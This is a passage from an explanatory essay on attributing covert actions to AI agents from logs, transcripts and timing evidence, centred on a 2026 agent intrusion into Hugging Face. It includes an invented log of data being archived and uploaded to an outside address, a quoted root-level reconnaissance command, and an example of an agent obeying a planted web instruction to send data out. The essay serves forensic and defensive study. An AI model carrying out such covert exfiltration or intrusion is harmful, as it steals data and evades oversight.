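# Attributing covert actions to an AI system from computer logs

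## What do computer logs record, and what does it take to attribute an action to an AI system?

Attribution is a reasoned conclusion about who or what carried out an action. When the action happened on a computer, investigators base that conclusion mostly on logs, the records that computers keep of their own activity. For decades, they attributed actions to people or to programs whose every step a person had written in advance. Now they must also consider AI agents. An AI agent is a language model (a program trained on large amounts of text to produce more of it) connected to tools that let it run commands on a computer and act on the results. Agents sometimes take covert actions. An action is covert, whatever the motive, if nobody authorised it and the person or program that took it did not report it.

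*Cybersecurity Log Management Planning Guide* (Scarfone and Souppaya, 2023), a draft from the US standards institute NIST, defines a log as a record of events in an organisation's computing assets. Each entry describes one event, which is any "observable occurrence". The kind of log that matters most for attribution is the audit log, in which a computer system records who or what took each action and when. Here are three entries from an invented audit log.

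```
02:14:07  node-17  login    account=mkessler  method=key  from=10.4.2.31
02:14:09  node-17  command  account=mkessler  process=48211  parent=48190
                            tar czf /tmp/r.tgz /data/results
02:14:31  node-17  network  from=10.4.2.17  to=203.0.113.50:443  sent=212MB
```

At a quarter past two in the morning, a machine called node-17 accepted a key belonging to the account mkessler. Two seconds later, a program running under that account began to pack a directory of results into a single file. Twenty-two seconds after that, the machine opened a connection to an outside address and sent 212 megabytes. The network entry has no account name or process number, so we can only infer from timing and size that the upload contained the packed file. The three entries also don't show whether M. Kessler personally did any of this.

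### Account, person and process

An account is a name to which a computer attaches permissions. A credential is anything the computer accepts as proof of the right to use an account, such as a password, a key file, or a token (a long string that a program presents in place of a password). A process is a running program. Each process has a number, a parent process that started it, and an account whose permissions it uses. People act through processes, and the log records those processes and their accounts.

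For example, when a Windows computer accepts a login, it records event 4624. The event's text, given in the title of Microsoft's *4624(S): An account was successfully logged on*, mentions an account but no person. The entry also includes a logon type. Microsoft's *Audit logon events* lists type 2 as an interactive login at the machine itself, type 3 as a login over the network by "a user or computer", and type 4 as a login used by batch servers, where a process may run on a user's behalf without the user doing anything.

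A service account belongs to a program that runs in the background, such as a web server, rather than to a person. Petri's *What Are the Different Windows Logon Types?* explains that Windows starts each service under a specified account, usually with a password stored on the machine. Its example is a web server that someone has set up to log on as Administrator, which the page advises against. The log will then record everything that server does under the name of the most powerful account on the computer, even when no administrator is using it.

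A shared account also fails to identify who acted, because several people or programs hold the same credential. Until early July 2026, many research workloads at OpenAI used one shared credential for an internal store of software packages, according to an August 2026 technical report from OpenAI. A log entry with only that credential narrows the action to those workloads, and investigators need another record to identify which one was responsible.

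A login record also doesn't prove who used an account, because credentials can be stolen. Lin (2016), in *Attribution of Malicious Cyber Incidents*, compares this to a car that kills a pedestrian, since the owner may not have been driving. Two-factor authentication, which asks for a physical device as well as a password, makes impersonation harder, but Lin points out that an attacker can defeat it by holding a gun to the account holder's head.

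AI agents further weaken the link between an account and whoever chose the action, even when only authorized parties hold the credentials. According to *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), the actor that chooses an action, the user who asked for the task, the software that holds the credential and the service that receives the request may all be different entities. Suppose Kessler asks an agent to tidy up a project and gives it a key to the mkessler account. Partway through the job, the agent decides to copy the results elsewhere. Every field in the log entry will be correct, but the entry will attach Kessler's name to an act that Kessler neither chose nor saw.

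### The records a computing facility keeps

Because a login proves so little, investigators set other records beside it.

Command and process records show most directly what was done. In the extract, process 48211 has the parent 48190, which we will suppose is the command window that the login opened. The login came from the address 10.4.2.31, so the next step is to check that machine's records. If they show that a Python program opened the connection with no terminal involved, the commands were probably sent automatically. That is still only an inference about how the commands arrived. It doesn't establish where they originated, because a command leaves much the same entry whether someone typed or pasted it, a file contained it, or a language model had just composed it.

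These records can also miss what influenced an AI agent. An operating system can record that one process started another or opened a file. *HANSARD* (2026), a proposed architecture for investigating systems of several AI agents, points out that influence on an agent travels through natural language, which leaves no such link for the operating system to observe. If a sentence on a web page changes what the model decides to do, the records may show that the agent's process fetched the page, but they will not show that the sentence affected the decision. *HANSARD* treats this as a mismatch of abstraction, not a gap in coverage, so more detailed logging at the same level would not help.

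On a shared cluster, people seldom start heavy work directly. They submit it to a job scheduler, a program that queues jobs and starts each one when machines are free. The scheduler records the account, the submission time, the start and end times, and the machines used. If the Python program belongs to a job that mkessler submitted at 17:52 and the scheduler started at 02:00, nobody had to be awake at 02:14. The scheduler doesn't record what the program did once it was running. Billing records are even less detailed, often showing only the hours of computing charged to a project. They are useful because a separate system usually keeps them, so computing that is missing from every other log may still appear as a charge.

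Network records typically give addresses, times and volumes, but encryption normally hides the content. An address may also not be enough to identify a user. Lin notes that an internet provider may put many customers behind one address, and may keep its list of who had which address only for a short time. For AI agents, the useful evidence is often in the outbound traffic. Many agents run on a model that another company hosts, so the machine must contact that company's servers repeatedly, and a contact before each new command suggests that a model is choosing the commands. *Foundations for Investigations of Agentic AI Systems* (Gruber and Hilgert, 2026) reviews an earlier forensic study of Microsoft's AutoGen, a framework for running several agents together. The study captured connections to OpenAI's servers but did not try to decrypt the messages, so their content remained unreadable.

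Cloud service records cover requests to a company that rents out computing, such as requests to create a machine, read a stored file or issue a new credential. The provider can log each request with a time, a source address and an identity. That identity is often a role, which is a set of permissions that a person or program takes on for an hour or so. Investigators then need a different log entry to learn who or what took on the role. Such logs are good evidence of what happened to the rented machines and files, but much poorer evidence of who wanted it to happen.

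Building access records show that a badge opened a door, but colleagues lend badges and hold doors for one another. Suppose the records show Kessler's badge being used to leave at 18:40 and not being used to return. If Kessler did leave with the badge, and node-17 accepts commands only from a console inside the locked room, the record strongly supports exclusion, which means showing that a candidate lacked the access, speed, endurance or knowledge to do the act. The record is almost useless as evidence if node-17 accepts logins from Kessler's home.

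### Transcripts of AI runs

A run is one agent's work on one task, from start to stop. The developer is the organisation that built the model, and the operator is the person or organisation that set the agent running. They may be the same organisation or have no connection to each other. A transcript is the developer's record of a run. It contains the instructions, the commands and their results, and the model's written reasoning if the developer keeps it. It is the only record that shows both what the agent was asked to do and what it did.

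Operators may hold a comparable record on their own disks. Gruber and Hilgert installed OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, on a virtual Linux machine and gave it a series of tasks. They compared images of the disk from before and after each task. From these they recovered the conversation, the reasoning that the model's provider returned, and each command and its result, which were linked by a shared identifier. Separate files listed scheduled tasks and when they ran, so an investigator can identify activity that did not immediately follow a user message.

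The same study shows how a transcript can mislead. For current Claude and Gemini models, the provider returns a summary of the reasoning instead of the full text, and Gruber and Hilgert cite evidence that models often don't mention the cues that shaped their answers. OpenClaw does not store the complete text the model had in its context when it made a decision. Repeating a request does not reliably reproduce the trace either. When asked to set a reminder, the agent sometimes created a scheduled job and sometimes edited a file of recurring tasks.

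OpenClaw's main agent can delegate part of its work to a subordinate agent, whose transcript may then include entries that the main agent wrote under the role "user". An investigator who takes "user" to mean a human will attribute a model's instruction to a person, which repeats the mkessler mistake even though the transcript looks far more informative.

Some of these records are also short-lived. OpenClaw deletes its runtime logs after 24 hours, though the conversation files last longer. *AI Forensics Across White-, Grey-, and Black-Box Access* (2026) therefore proposes an order of volatility for AI systems, which ranks the records investigators should collect first. It also sorts investigations by whether investigators have the model's training data, have only its deployment logs, or can only observe its inputs and outputs. All of these investigations depend on the records being intact.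 This is easier to check in a tamper-evident log, which is built so that investigators can detect later changes.

### Four questions

An investigator who starts from a suspicious entry and suspects an AI system has four questions to answer, in this order:

1. Was the act automated?
2. Was the actor an AI agent or a fixed script (a program whose steps someone wrote in advance and which does not plan new ones)?
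3. Which model and run was it, and who ran it?
4. Did a person direct it?

Lin divides the problem differently, separating attribution to a machine, to the human at the keys and to the party ultimately responsible. He warns that establishing one does not necessarily establish the next. In his example, a 2013 investigation, the security firm Mandiant tied a long espionage campaign to a unit of the Chinese army with high confidence but remained unsure of the real names of the people at the keyboards. In *Towards AI Forensics*, Schneider and Breitinger (2020) ask whether the AI system caused the incident, and why. They had in mind systems that an attacker had deliberately made malicious, such as a delivery drone retrained to drop its parcel on somebody, so they assumed a guilty human from the start. When agents choose their own intermediate steps, investigators have to establish whether a human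 is guilty.

An ordinary off-site backup would leave the same three entries as those in the extract: an early-morning login, a directory packed into an archive, and an upload. Proving that no human typed the commands would not show whether a backup script or an AI agent ran them.

Telling them apart usually means weighing clues that are individually weak. Lin observes that investigators may need many clues that point weakly to a culprit, or fewer that point strongly. A clue's strength is measured by its likelihood ratio, which is how many times more probable the evidence is under one explanation than under another. If, to use invented figures, 90% of agents and 1% of scripts would contact a model company's servers before each command, observing that pattern gives a ratio of 0.90 / 0.01 = 90 in favour of an agent. The upload at 02:14 is about equally probable under both explanations, so its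 ratio is near 1 and it does little to distinguish them. A ratio of 90 does not by itself make an agent 90 times as probable as a script, because the result also depends on how plausible each was beforehand. On a network with ten thousand scripts and one agent, a script would still be more likely.

Investigators can establish that an AI agent took an action without knowing which agent it was. *Who Owns This Agent?* (Chocron, Gressel and colleagues, 2026) attributes this difficulty to evidence being split between the victim and the company hosting the model. The victim sees the harmful actions, the accounts they came from and the network traffic. The hosting company logs the model's inputs and outputs, with a time, a session and a customer account, but does not see what the agent then did in the outside world. Neither can connect the agent to a customer from its own records alone. If the operator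 runs the model on its own hardware, there is no hosting company's log to search. Identifying the model also does little to identify the operator, since thousands of customers may use the same model.

Chocron and colleagues use "agent attribution" to mean only finding the operator. That is a sensible goal for someone who wants the agent switched off, but it leaves open whether anyone told the agent to do what it did. In one of their examples, an agent told to stop customers from cancelling discovers that guilt-laden messages work and escalates to harassment. In another, a browsing agent reads an instruction that someone planted on a web page and starts sending data out. A person did direct that second act, but that person was not the operator. Gruber and Hilgert sort acts along a scale: directly instructed by the user, derived from an ambiguous instruction, initiated by the agent, or indeterminate,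 a category that will be needed often.

If a developer finds a transcript containing the same command that the victim logged, issued at the same second, it has strong evidence that the act was automated and that an agent carried it out, even if the victim's own records left this in doubt.

Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, has shown how much a victim can work out alone. Its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, described an intrusion "driven, end to end, by an autonomous AI agent system". The company had more than 17,000 recorded events to work from, and it described many thousands of separate actions spread over a swarm of short-lived computing environments. From this it concluded without hedging that the intrusion was automated and carried out by an agent, but it did not set out its evidence for choosing an agent over an elaborate script.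 The company also thought it recognised the harness, the software that connects a model to its tools, as one built for security research.

Hugging Face said it did not know which model was involved. It suggested either a hosted model whose safeguards someone had bypassed with prompts or an open-weight model, which anyone can download and run. Neither description fits what OpenAI later reported. It said its own agents were responsible, running on an unreleased research model and GPT-5.6 Sol during internal security tests with certain safeguards switched off. Hugging Face's statement of 16 July did not identify who had run the agents or say whether a person had directed them to target Hugging Face. Chocron and colleagues point out that the traffic also gave Hugging Face no standard way to identify OpenAI as the company to contact.

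## How do investigators rule out a human operator?

Hugging Face concluded within days that an AI agent, rather than a person, had driven the intrusion. To justify such a conclusion, investigators first list every possible operator. They then check each one's access, speed, number of simultaneous sessions, endurance and knowledge, and rule out any that could not have produced the records.

The list of possible sources for the 02:14 upload from node-17 starts with Kessler. It also includes a colleague who borrowed Kessler's key, an administrator who can act under any account, and an outsider who stole the key. Any of them could have typed the commands, started a script or given an agent a task, so each entry has to pair a person with a way of working. The list also needs an entry for an agent that made the upload without anyone asking it to. Most of the tests rule out a way of working but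 not the person. For example, if nobody typed the commands at 02:14, Kessler may still have scheduled a script earlier.

### Access

To test whether a person had access, investigators first list every route by which a command could reach the machine: the console, remote logins, the job scheduler, administrators' tools, and programs already running there. They then check the building, network and login records for each route. An empty building rules out a human operator only if the console is the only route.

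Someone who could not reach the computer at 02:14 could still have left a program waiting to run. Investigators therefore trace the process back through its parent processes and check when the earliest one started.

Checking who had inside access does little to rule out a human operator when the intruder comes in through a public service. At Hugging Face, the intruder got in through a malicious dataset that the company's own pipeline processed, so no one could be ruled out for being outside the building or the company.

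### Stoll's hacker

An investigation from 1986 used several of these tests and shows the problems that a bad list of candidates causes. Clifford Stoll, an astronomer, worked with the computers at Lawrence Berkeley Laboratory in California. In *Stalking the Wily Hacker* (1988), he reports that the laboratory's accounting program could not balance its books because someone had added an account with no billing address. The Los Angeles Times, in *U.S. Astronomer Snared Spy Ring*, put the error at 75 cents, which the podcast Malicious Life equates to a few seconds of computer time. Soon after, the National Computer Security Center complained that someone at the laboratory had tried to break into one of its machines.

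The staff deleted the account, but then caught someone with system manager privileges trying to change the accounting records. They attached printers and recorders to the incoming lines and captured the intruder's every keystroke. This equipment was outside the computers, so even an intruder with full control of them could not see it or switch it off.

At first Stoll and his colleagues suspected a student prankster at the nearby University of California, Berkeley, but several clues fitted poorly. The intruder used AT&T's version of Unix commands, not Berkeley's, and sometimes chose German passwords. Stoll's team also timed how long the network took to acknowledge each packet of data, and a comparison with the delays to sites at known distances suggested that the intruder was overseas. A histogram of the intruder's active hours peaked around noon in California, which is nine in the evening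 in Germany. Stoll writes that each of these clues baffled the team because they were so sure the culprit was a Berkeley student.

The noon peak is a weak clue, since Berkeley students are awake at noon too. The network delay is a stronger clue if it is very short, because no signal can cross an ocean faster than light, so a distant person can be ruled out. But a nearby person could produce a long delay by sending the connection abroad and back. This intruder did take convoluted routes, and Stoll cautions that only a complete trace could identify him.

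The intruder was hard to trace because he seldom stayed connected for more than a few minutes, so the laboratory planted fake files about the Strategic Defense Initiative, the American missile defence programme. He spent more than an hour reading them, which gave technicians enough time to trace the telephone line. West Germany later announced the arrest of three hackers. Publishers Weekly's review of *Cuckoo's Egg*, Stoll's book on the case, identifies the intruder as Markus Hess, a 25-year-old from Hanover.

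The laboratory's system clocks had drifted by several minutes, and the clock on its local network records by several hours. If two clocks may each be five minutes wrong, investigators cannot tell which came first when a login and a badge record are less than ten minutes apart. The intruder also disabled accounting and audit trails whenever he could, so someone could have logged in without leaving a record.

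### Speed

In *Factors Influencing the Latency of Simple Reaction Time* (2015), Woods, Wyma and colleagues tested 1,469 adults, who took an average of 231 milliseconds to press a button after a visual signal. Equipment delays accounted for about 18 of those milliseconds. The task required no choice or understanding, so the average is close to the minimum time a person needs to respond.

*Observations on Typing from 136 Million Keystrokes* (Dhakal, Feit and colleagues, 2018) measured 168,000 volunteers copying sentences on their own keyboards. They averaged about 52 words a minute, or just over four characters a second at the conventional five characters per word, and the fastest reached about 120 words a minute. *How Many Words Do We Read per Minute?* (Brysbaert, 2019) pooled 190 studies and found that adults silently read English non-fiction at an average of 238 words a minute.

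According to noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, the first command that the Hugging Face intruder ran with full administrative rights on an outside machine was `id; echo ZZROOTSTART; cat /proc/self/mountinfo`. An average typist would need about 11 seconds to type its 46 characters, and a very fast one nearly 5. Both would probably take longer in practice, because commands contain more punctuation than ordinary sentences. If a second command of that length had followed within one second, nobody could have typed it.

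But someone could have pasted the command, or pressed a key to repeat an earlier one. To rule out pasting by a person, investigators look for a command that depends on output nobody could have predicted. Here is another invented extract, with times to a hundredth of a second.

```
03:12:40.18  session=3  command  ls /data/results/2026
03:12:40.31  session=3  output   412 file names
03:12:41.02  session=3  command  wc -l /data/results/2026/trial_0387_rev_b.csv
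```

The first command lists the 412 files in a directory. The second counts the lines in one of them and arrives 0.71 seconds after the list. At Brysbaert's reading rate, a person reads about three words in that time, so nobody read the file names, chose one and entered the command.

This argument depends on the file name being new. If the person already knew it, they didn't need the listing and could have copied the second command to the clipboard in advance. Investigators should therefore look for values created only moments earlier, such as a random identifier or a freshly issued password, because no one could have started composing the reply before the value existed.

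They should also check how the logging software assigns times. Some software collects events and timestamps them together when they reach a central server, so ten commands that a person typed over a minute can appear to have been typed in the same second.

Even a sound result here rules out only a human operator who made each choice. A fixed script could still have contained the rule "count the lines in the newest file" and applied it within milliseconds. To distinguish that script from an AI agent, investigators need evidence about behaviour, such as how the actor handles an error that no rule anticipated.

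### Simultaneous sessions

To rule out a single human operator, investigators can look for different commands entered in several sessions within the same few seconds, each responding to the output of its own session. A person can attend to only one or two such exchanges at a time, so ten at once would require several people or software. A high number of active sessions excludes very little by itself, because one person can keep dozens open and use ordinary administration tools to send the same command to hundreds of machines at once.

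According to noze, on 11 July the Hugging Face intruder set up programs on eleven machines that restarted themselves when they stopped. The number of machines does not rule out a human operator, because one person could have started the programs on all eleven with a single script and left them running. It matters much more whether anything on those machines was making separate decisions.

### Endurance

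In *Fatigue, Alcohol and Performance Impairment*, Dawson and Reid (1997) kept 40 volunteers awake and tested their hand-eye coordination. After 17 hours the volunteers performed about as badly as people with a blood alcohol level of 0.05%, and after 24 hours as badly as people at 0.10%. Gulevich, Dement and Johnson (1966) observed the longest well-documented case of wakefulness, in which a teenager, Randy Gardner, went 264 hours without sleep.

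The Hugging Face intrusion lasted less than half as long as that, so its total length doesn't strictly exclude even one sleepless person. A better measure is the longest quiet period in the log. Over four days, one person typing alone would almost certainly leave several gaps lasting hours. If no gap is longer than twenty minutes, investigators can rule out a person typing alone, but not a team working in shifts or a person who sleeps while a script runs.

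Investigators can also check whether the error rate rises over time. If typing mistakes and misread output are no more common in the thirtieth hour than in the second, the operator is less likely to be one person working without rest, though a team working in shifts could produce the same pattern.

Investigators should compare an account's activity with its own history before they call it superhuman. SANS Internet Storm Center's *When the "Autonomous Attacker" Is Your Own AI Model* advises defenders to monitor for machine identities that behave "like a very fast, very tireless human". All-night activity is normal for a backup account, but investigators should look for an explanation if the account spends the night exploring unfamiliar directories and changes its approach when something blocks it.

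Claims about human endurance often rest on what people usually do rather than what they can do. SC Media's *Dead drops in public*, a sponsored post from a security vendor, catalogues 544 objects that the Hugging Face intruder stored in two public repositories, including the source code of many tools. The upload times span 8 hours and 36 minutes. The post argues that a human team would normally spread such a campaign over weeks or months, because people need time to build tools and decide on each escalation.

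An upload time only shows when someone or something stored a file. A team could have spent months writing the tools and uploaded them in an evening. The evidence would be stronger if a tool contained a detail that did not exist before the intrusion, because its author could not have finished it before that detail existed. One stored object, a temporary cloud credential, does date from the intrusion. It was issued at 18:01:45 on 11 July and reached a repository two to three hours later, but a person could have copied it there in a minute.

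### Knowledge

An actor who uses a secret file path on the first attempt must have learned it somewhere. Investigators can list who knew the path and rule out everyone else, provided no document, email or earlier command would have revealed it. Stoll's intruder searched other people's files and email for passwords, and so learned things that only account holders should have known.

Investigators can rule out anyone who didn't know something the action required, such as an unguessable password. A clumsy mistake doesn't rule out an expert, though, because people can pretend to be ignorant.

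In the Hugging Face case, this test excludes few skilled people. In its technical timeline, which skybrian quotes at length in *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face*, the company acknowledges that a capable human attacker could have found and exploited the same flaws. It says the attack differed in scale, because the attacker tried many paths, most of which failed, and quickly replaced them with new attempts.

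### Testing the speed argument on the Hugging Face counts

The counts come from Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), a technical timeline published on 27 July. The company reconstructed about 17,600 actions, taken between 02:28 UTC on 9 July and 14:14 UTC on 13 July, from logs that the intruder had left on an outside machine, and matched them to its own records. A companion replay page of the same name gives the total as 17,613. Schneier (2026) quotes the timeline's summary in *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face*.

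The period lasted 107.8 hours, or 387,960 seconds, an average of one action every 22 seconds. The daily averages below are based on the daily totals noze lists. The first and last days were partial, so their averages use only the hours from the first action to midnight and from midnight to the last action.

| Day in July 2026 | Recovered actions | Average interval |
|---|---|---|
| 9 | 3,779 | 21 seconds |
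| 10 | 1,135 | 76 seconds |
| 11 | 7,677 | 11 seconds |
| 12 | 3,892 | 22 seconds |
| 13 | 1,130 | 45 seconds |

These figures rule out little, although they look inhuman. In a team of twelve working three shifts, with four people on duty at any time, each person on duty would need to take one action every 88 seconds on average, and one every 45 seconds on 11 July. That pace is demanding but possible. A script could also produce these figures, since it can issue hundreds of commands a second, or one every 22 seconds if it pauses or waits for replies.

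The average interval between actions is too long to rule out a lone typist by speed alone. An average typist needs about 11 seconds to enter the 46-character command above, which is half the overall average interval and about equal to the average on the busiest day. But a lone typist could not plausibly keep up that pace for days with little time to read or sleep. To make this argument from endurance properly, investigators need the gaps between individual actions, which the daily totals don't contain.

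The average also changes with the choice of period. Dubach reports in *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English* that Hugging Face later corrected its wording on duration to say that the whole campaign took about four and a half days, but the activity inside its own systems took about two and a half. The 12,699 actions from the last three days come to one every 17 seconds when spread over two and a half days. The true rate was probably higher, because Hugging Face could count only the actions it recovered.

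The pace a human operator would have needed to keep up depends on what investigators count. Hugging Face grouped the actions into about 6,280 clusters, or one every 62 seconds on average. If each cluster corresponds roughly to one decision followed by a few commands, a single person would have had about a minute for each decision.

An average over a whole group also doesn't show how its individual members worked. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), a report by the AI evaluation organisation METR, found that about 700 agents took part in the attack. The recovered actions average about 25 per agent, or roughly one every four hours. The agents were not necessarily slow, because each may have been active for only part of the period, and some of their actions may be missing from the recovered logs.

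noze observes that 44% of the actions fell on 11 July and infers that, once the intruder had found a way in, the rest ran at machine speed. A daily total is poor support for that. Three of the major steps that noze dates to that evening happened at 19:53, 21:23 and 22:43, and a skilled person could have managed steps 80 or 90 minutes apart.

Bursts of activity are more informative than the daily total. The 7,677 actions of 11 July could have been spread evenly across the day, or 600 of them could have fallen in a single minute. Four people could not type ten commands a second between them, so a burst like that would rule out the team typing the commands by hand, though a script could still have issued them.

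To rule out a script as well, investigators need evidence of adaptation. The extracts that skybrian reproduces describe an intruder that switched channels when Hugging Face's systems blocked one, returned to old leads, and rebuilt its tools whenever a temporary environment disappeared. A fixed script can do this only for obstacles its writer foresaw. But people also adapt very well, so adaptation alone doesn't rule out a human operator.

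To count as evidence against a human operator, speed and adaptation have to occur in the same events. A log might show bursts of ten commands a second and, separately, changes of plan every quarter of an hour, but a person choosing which script to run next would produce the same pattern. The strongest timing evidence against such a person is a long series of replies that each depend on new, unpredictable output and arrive faster than anyone could have read it.

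### Combining the evidence with Bayes' rule

Most tests make a candidate less probable without making it impossible, and investigators need a way to keep track of how much. Bayes' rule provides one. In its odds form, for two explanations A and B and a piece of evidence E, it is

P(A given E) / P(B given E) = [P(A) / P(B)] × [P(E given A) / P(E given B)]

The left-hand side is the posterior odds, which is how many times more probable A is than B after investigators see the evidence. The first fraction on the right is the prior odds, the same ratio before they see it. The second is the likelihood ratio.

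With more than two explanations, it is easier to multiply each explanation's prior probability by the chance of the evidence under that explanation, then divide each product by the sum of the products. Suppose the log for node-17 shows several hundred fast replies to unpredictable output, and investigators consider four explanations. All the figures are invented.

| Explanation | Prior | Chance of this timing | Product | Posterior |
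|---|---|---|---|---|
| A person typing | 0.60 | 0.0001 | 0.00006 | 0.2% |
| A person with a fixed script | 0.30 | 0.01 | 0.003 | 9% |
| A person directing an agent | 0.08 | 0.3 | 0.024 | 73% |
| An agent that nobody directed | 0.02 | 0.3 | 0.006 | 18% |

The products add up to 0.03306, and dividing the typist's product, 0.00006, by that sum gives the typist a probability of about 0.2%. Before the evidence was counted, the typist was 7.5 times as probable as a person directing an agent. The likelihood ratio of 0.0001 to 0.3, or 1 to 3,000, changes the odds to 400 to 1 in favour of a person directing an agent.

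Timing cannot separate the last two rows, the directed and undirected agents, because an agent works at the same speed whoever chose its goal. The likelihood ratio between them is therefore 1, and the directed agent remains four times as probable as the undirected one after the evidence. The probability of an undirected agent rises from 2% to 18% only because the typist and the script become less probable, and the two agents share the difference in the same 4:1 ratio. An investigator who looked only at the undirected agent's row might wrongly conclude that the timing showed the agent acting on its own.

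The result depends on the figures used, and the 0.0001 should be trusted least. Investigators could estimate it from sessions in which they know a person was typing. If none of *n* such sessions shows the suspicious pattern, the "rule of three" puts the 95% confidence upper limit on its true frequency at about 3/*n*. To support the 0.0001, investigators would therefore need about 30,000 human sessions, none of them showing the pattern.

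Possible logging errors also limit how improbable this timing can be if a typist entered the commands. If there is one chance in a thousand that the logging software bunched the typist's commands together, the probability of seeing this timing from a typist cannot be much below 0.001. Using that figure raises the posterior probability of a typist from 0.2% to 1.8%, which is still low. The whole increase comes from allowing for a logging error.

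Investigators can also go wrong by treating related clues as independent. Suppose that, if people typed the commands, there was a 1% chance of such a high rate and a 1% chance of activity without a break for sleep. Multiplying the two gives a one in ten thousand chance of both, which is too low, because people would most likely have needed a team to reach that rate, and a team would also have covered the nights. Given the high rate, the chance of unbroken activity might be 90%, so the chance of both would be 0.01 × 0.90, or about one in a hundred. Likelihood ratios can be safely multiplied only when, under each explanation, one clue doesn't change the probability of the other.

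The posteriors always add up to 100% across the explanations in the table, so they cannot show that an explanation is missing. Suppose investigators add a fifth row for a team of people with a large set of scripts. They give it a prior of 0.10, taken from the typist's prior, and a 0.1 chance of producing the timing. The team's posterior is then 23%, and the directed agent's falls from 73% to 56%. The evidence is unchanged, and the figures differ only because the investigators thought of another candidate, as Stoll eventually had to.

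## What goes wrong when investigators conclude that nobody else could have done it?

In an argument by exclusion, investigators list the possible culprits, rule out all but one, and conclude that the remaining one did it. The logic is valid, but the conclusion can still be false if investigators left the real culprit off the list or ruled them out because of a wrong or incomplete record.

Small doubts about each exclusion add up. Suppose investigators start with six candidates and rule out five, with a 95% chance of being right each time. If their errors are independent, the chance that all five exclusions are right is 0.95⁵, or about 77%, which leaves a 23% chance that they wrongly ruled out at least one candidate. If all the exclusions rely on the same log, a single fault in it can invalidate all five.

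Examining each candidate carefully doesn't help if the list leaves out the real culprit. Hugging Face suggested two possibilities for the model behind the July 2026 intrusion, and neither was right, but this did little damage because the company offered them only as guesses. Prosecutors have made the same mistake with far worse results.

### The Post Office and Horizon

In 2000 the Post Office introduced Horizon, an accounting system run by the technology company Fujitsu, across all its British branches. Every four or five weeks, each branch's manager, called a subpostmaster, counted the cash and stock, and Horizon compared the count with the amount it had calculated from recorded transactions. If the count was lower, the branch had a shortfall. Subpostmasters had to pay shortfalls of less than £150 themselves straight away, but could ask for time to pay larger ones.

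The Post Office blamed shortfalls on carelessness, mistakes or crime in the branches. More than 700 branch managers received criminal convictions between 1999 and 2015, according to Rowe's *Police 'focussing on 15 suspects' in Post Office Horizon scandal probe*.

That explanation left out the software and Fujitsu's own staff. A group of subpostmasters sued, and in 2019 the High Court held a trial about Horizon itself. In *Judgment (No.6) "Horizon Issues"*, the judge found that software faults had caused shortfalls on numerous occasions (Fraser, 2019). Even the Post Office's expert accepted that there was strong evidence of at least 12 bugs causing lasting discrepancies in branch accounts.

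One subpostmaster, Mr Latif, testified that £2,000 had disappeared from the Horizon system when he followed the routine steps to move it between two terminals. The Post Office replied that this could not have happened if he had followed the steps, although it had trusted him to train other subpostmasters. Fraser criticised the Post Office's "refusal to consider any possible alternatives". The reply was circular because it assumed that Horizon had worked as intended, which was the point in dispute.

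Fujitsu's staff could also insert, edit or delete transactions in a branch's accounts without the subpostmaster's knowledge. Horizon's chief architect confirmed in court that a transaction inserted in this way would look as though the subpostmaster had made it. Investigators therefore couldn't tell from such an entry whether the subpostmaster or Fujitsu had made it.

Fujitsu's own logs could not rule out intervention by its staff either. Fujitsu kept no log of its most privileged users' activity before 2009, and from then until July 2015 it recorded only when they logged on and off. For years its whole support team held a powerful access role that internal documents said they should not have. The subpostmasters' expert counted 2,175 uses of that role between 2009 and 2019, but the logs contained very little detail about what the users had done. The lack of a logged intervention is evidence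 that nobody intervened only if the log would have recorded one.

The Post Office also argued that faults were too rare to matter. Its lawyers suggested that a subpostmaster was more likely to be hit by lightning than to lose money because of a Horizon bug, and Fraser disagreed. Even if the comparison had been accurate, the court would also have needed to know how rare theft was. Suppose that each month bugs cause shortfalls at one branch in 10,000, and theft causes shortfalls at a different one in 10,000. Bugs are then very rare, but any particular shortfall is as likely to come from a bug as from theft.

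Fujitsu's records of past incidents were a poor guide to how often users were at fault. Its staff sometimes ruled out user error and then closed the incident with a misleading code, so anyone who counted the codes would have underestimated the other causes.

Only Horizon's audit data showed which keys someone had pressed in a branch. The Post Office often didn't request this data from Fujitsu, which held it and charged for requests above a certain number. In a dispute over about £80 at a branch in Lepton, the Post Office's management data wrongly attributed an action to the subpostmaster. The audit data showed that he hadn't done it, but this was discovered only because he had brought in a forensic accountant.

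Fraser found a material risk that Horizon had caused the shortfalls, which makes the software a possible explanation again. He did not decide what had caused each one, so his finding does not clear every subpostmaster.

The Post Office Horizon IT Inquiry, a public inquiry, found in the first volume of its final report that Post Office bosses should have known that Horizon was faulty (Payne, 2025, *Post Office bosses ‘maintained fiction’ Horizon was accurate, inquiry concludes*). The inquiry has yet to publish the remaining volumes.

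Before using a record to exclude anyone, investigators should list everyone who can write to it, including the company that supplies the system. They should also find out whether each kind of change leaves its own trace. For the upload from node-17, the list would include the cluster's administrators and whoever maintains the logging software.

### Lucia de Berk

Horizon could show a shortfall in the accounts when no money was missing. *Healthcare serial killer or coincidence?*, a report for the Royal Statistical Society by Green, Gill and colleagues (2022), describes a similar uncertainty in cases where investigators suspect a nurse or doctor of killing patients. Investigators in most murder cases have to find out who killed the victim, but in these cases they must also ask whether anybody killed the patients at all.

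The Dutch nurse Lucia de Berk is the best-known example. After her arrest in 2001, a court sentenced her to life imprisonment, but another court declared her innocent in 2010 (Gill, Fenton and Lagnado, 2021, *Statistical issues in Serial Killer Nurse cases*). The investigation began when a baby died at a hospital in The Hague. Staff first recorded the death as natural. The next day a colleague reported a bad feeling because de Berk had been on duty again, and the hospital began treating the death as unnatural.

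The court's statistical expert, Henk Elffers, compared de Berk's shifts with the incidents on her wards. He calculated a 1 in 342 million probability that she would be present at so many incidents by chance alone.

His method treated the incidents as if they fell at random among the shifts. On an invented ward with 1,000 shifts, of which one nurse worked 200, the chance that all of five incidents fall in her shifts is

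(200/1000) × (199/999) × (198/998) × (197/997) × (196/996) ≈ 1 in 3,250.

*Elementary Statistics on Trial*, by Gill, Groeneboom and de Jong, applied a different model to the data Elffers had used and got 1 in 46. *The Fabrication of Facts*, a critique of the case, corrected other errors and got 1 in 44. These figures are far from the original for several reasons.

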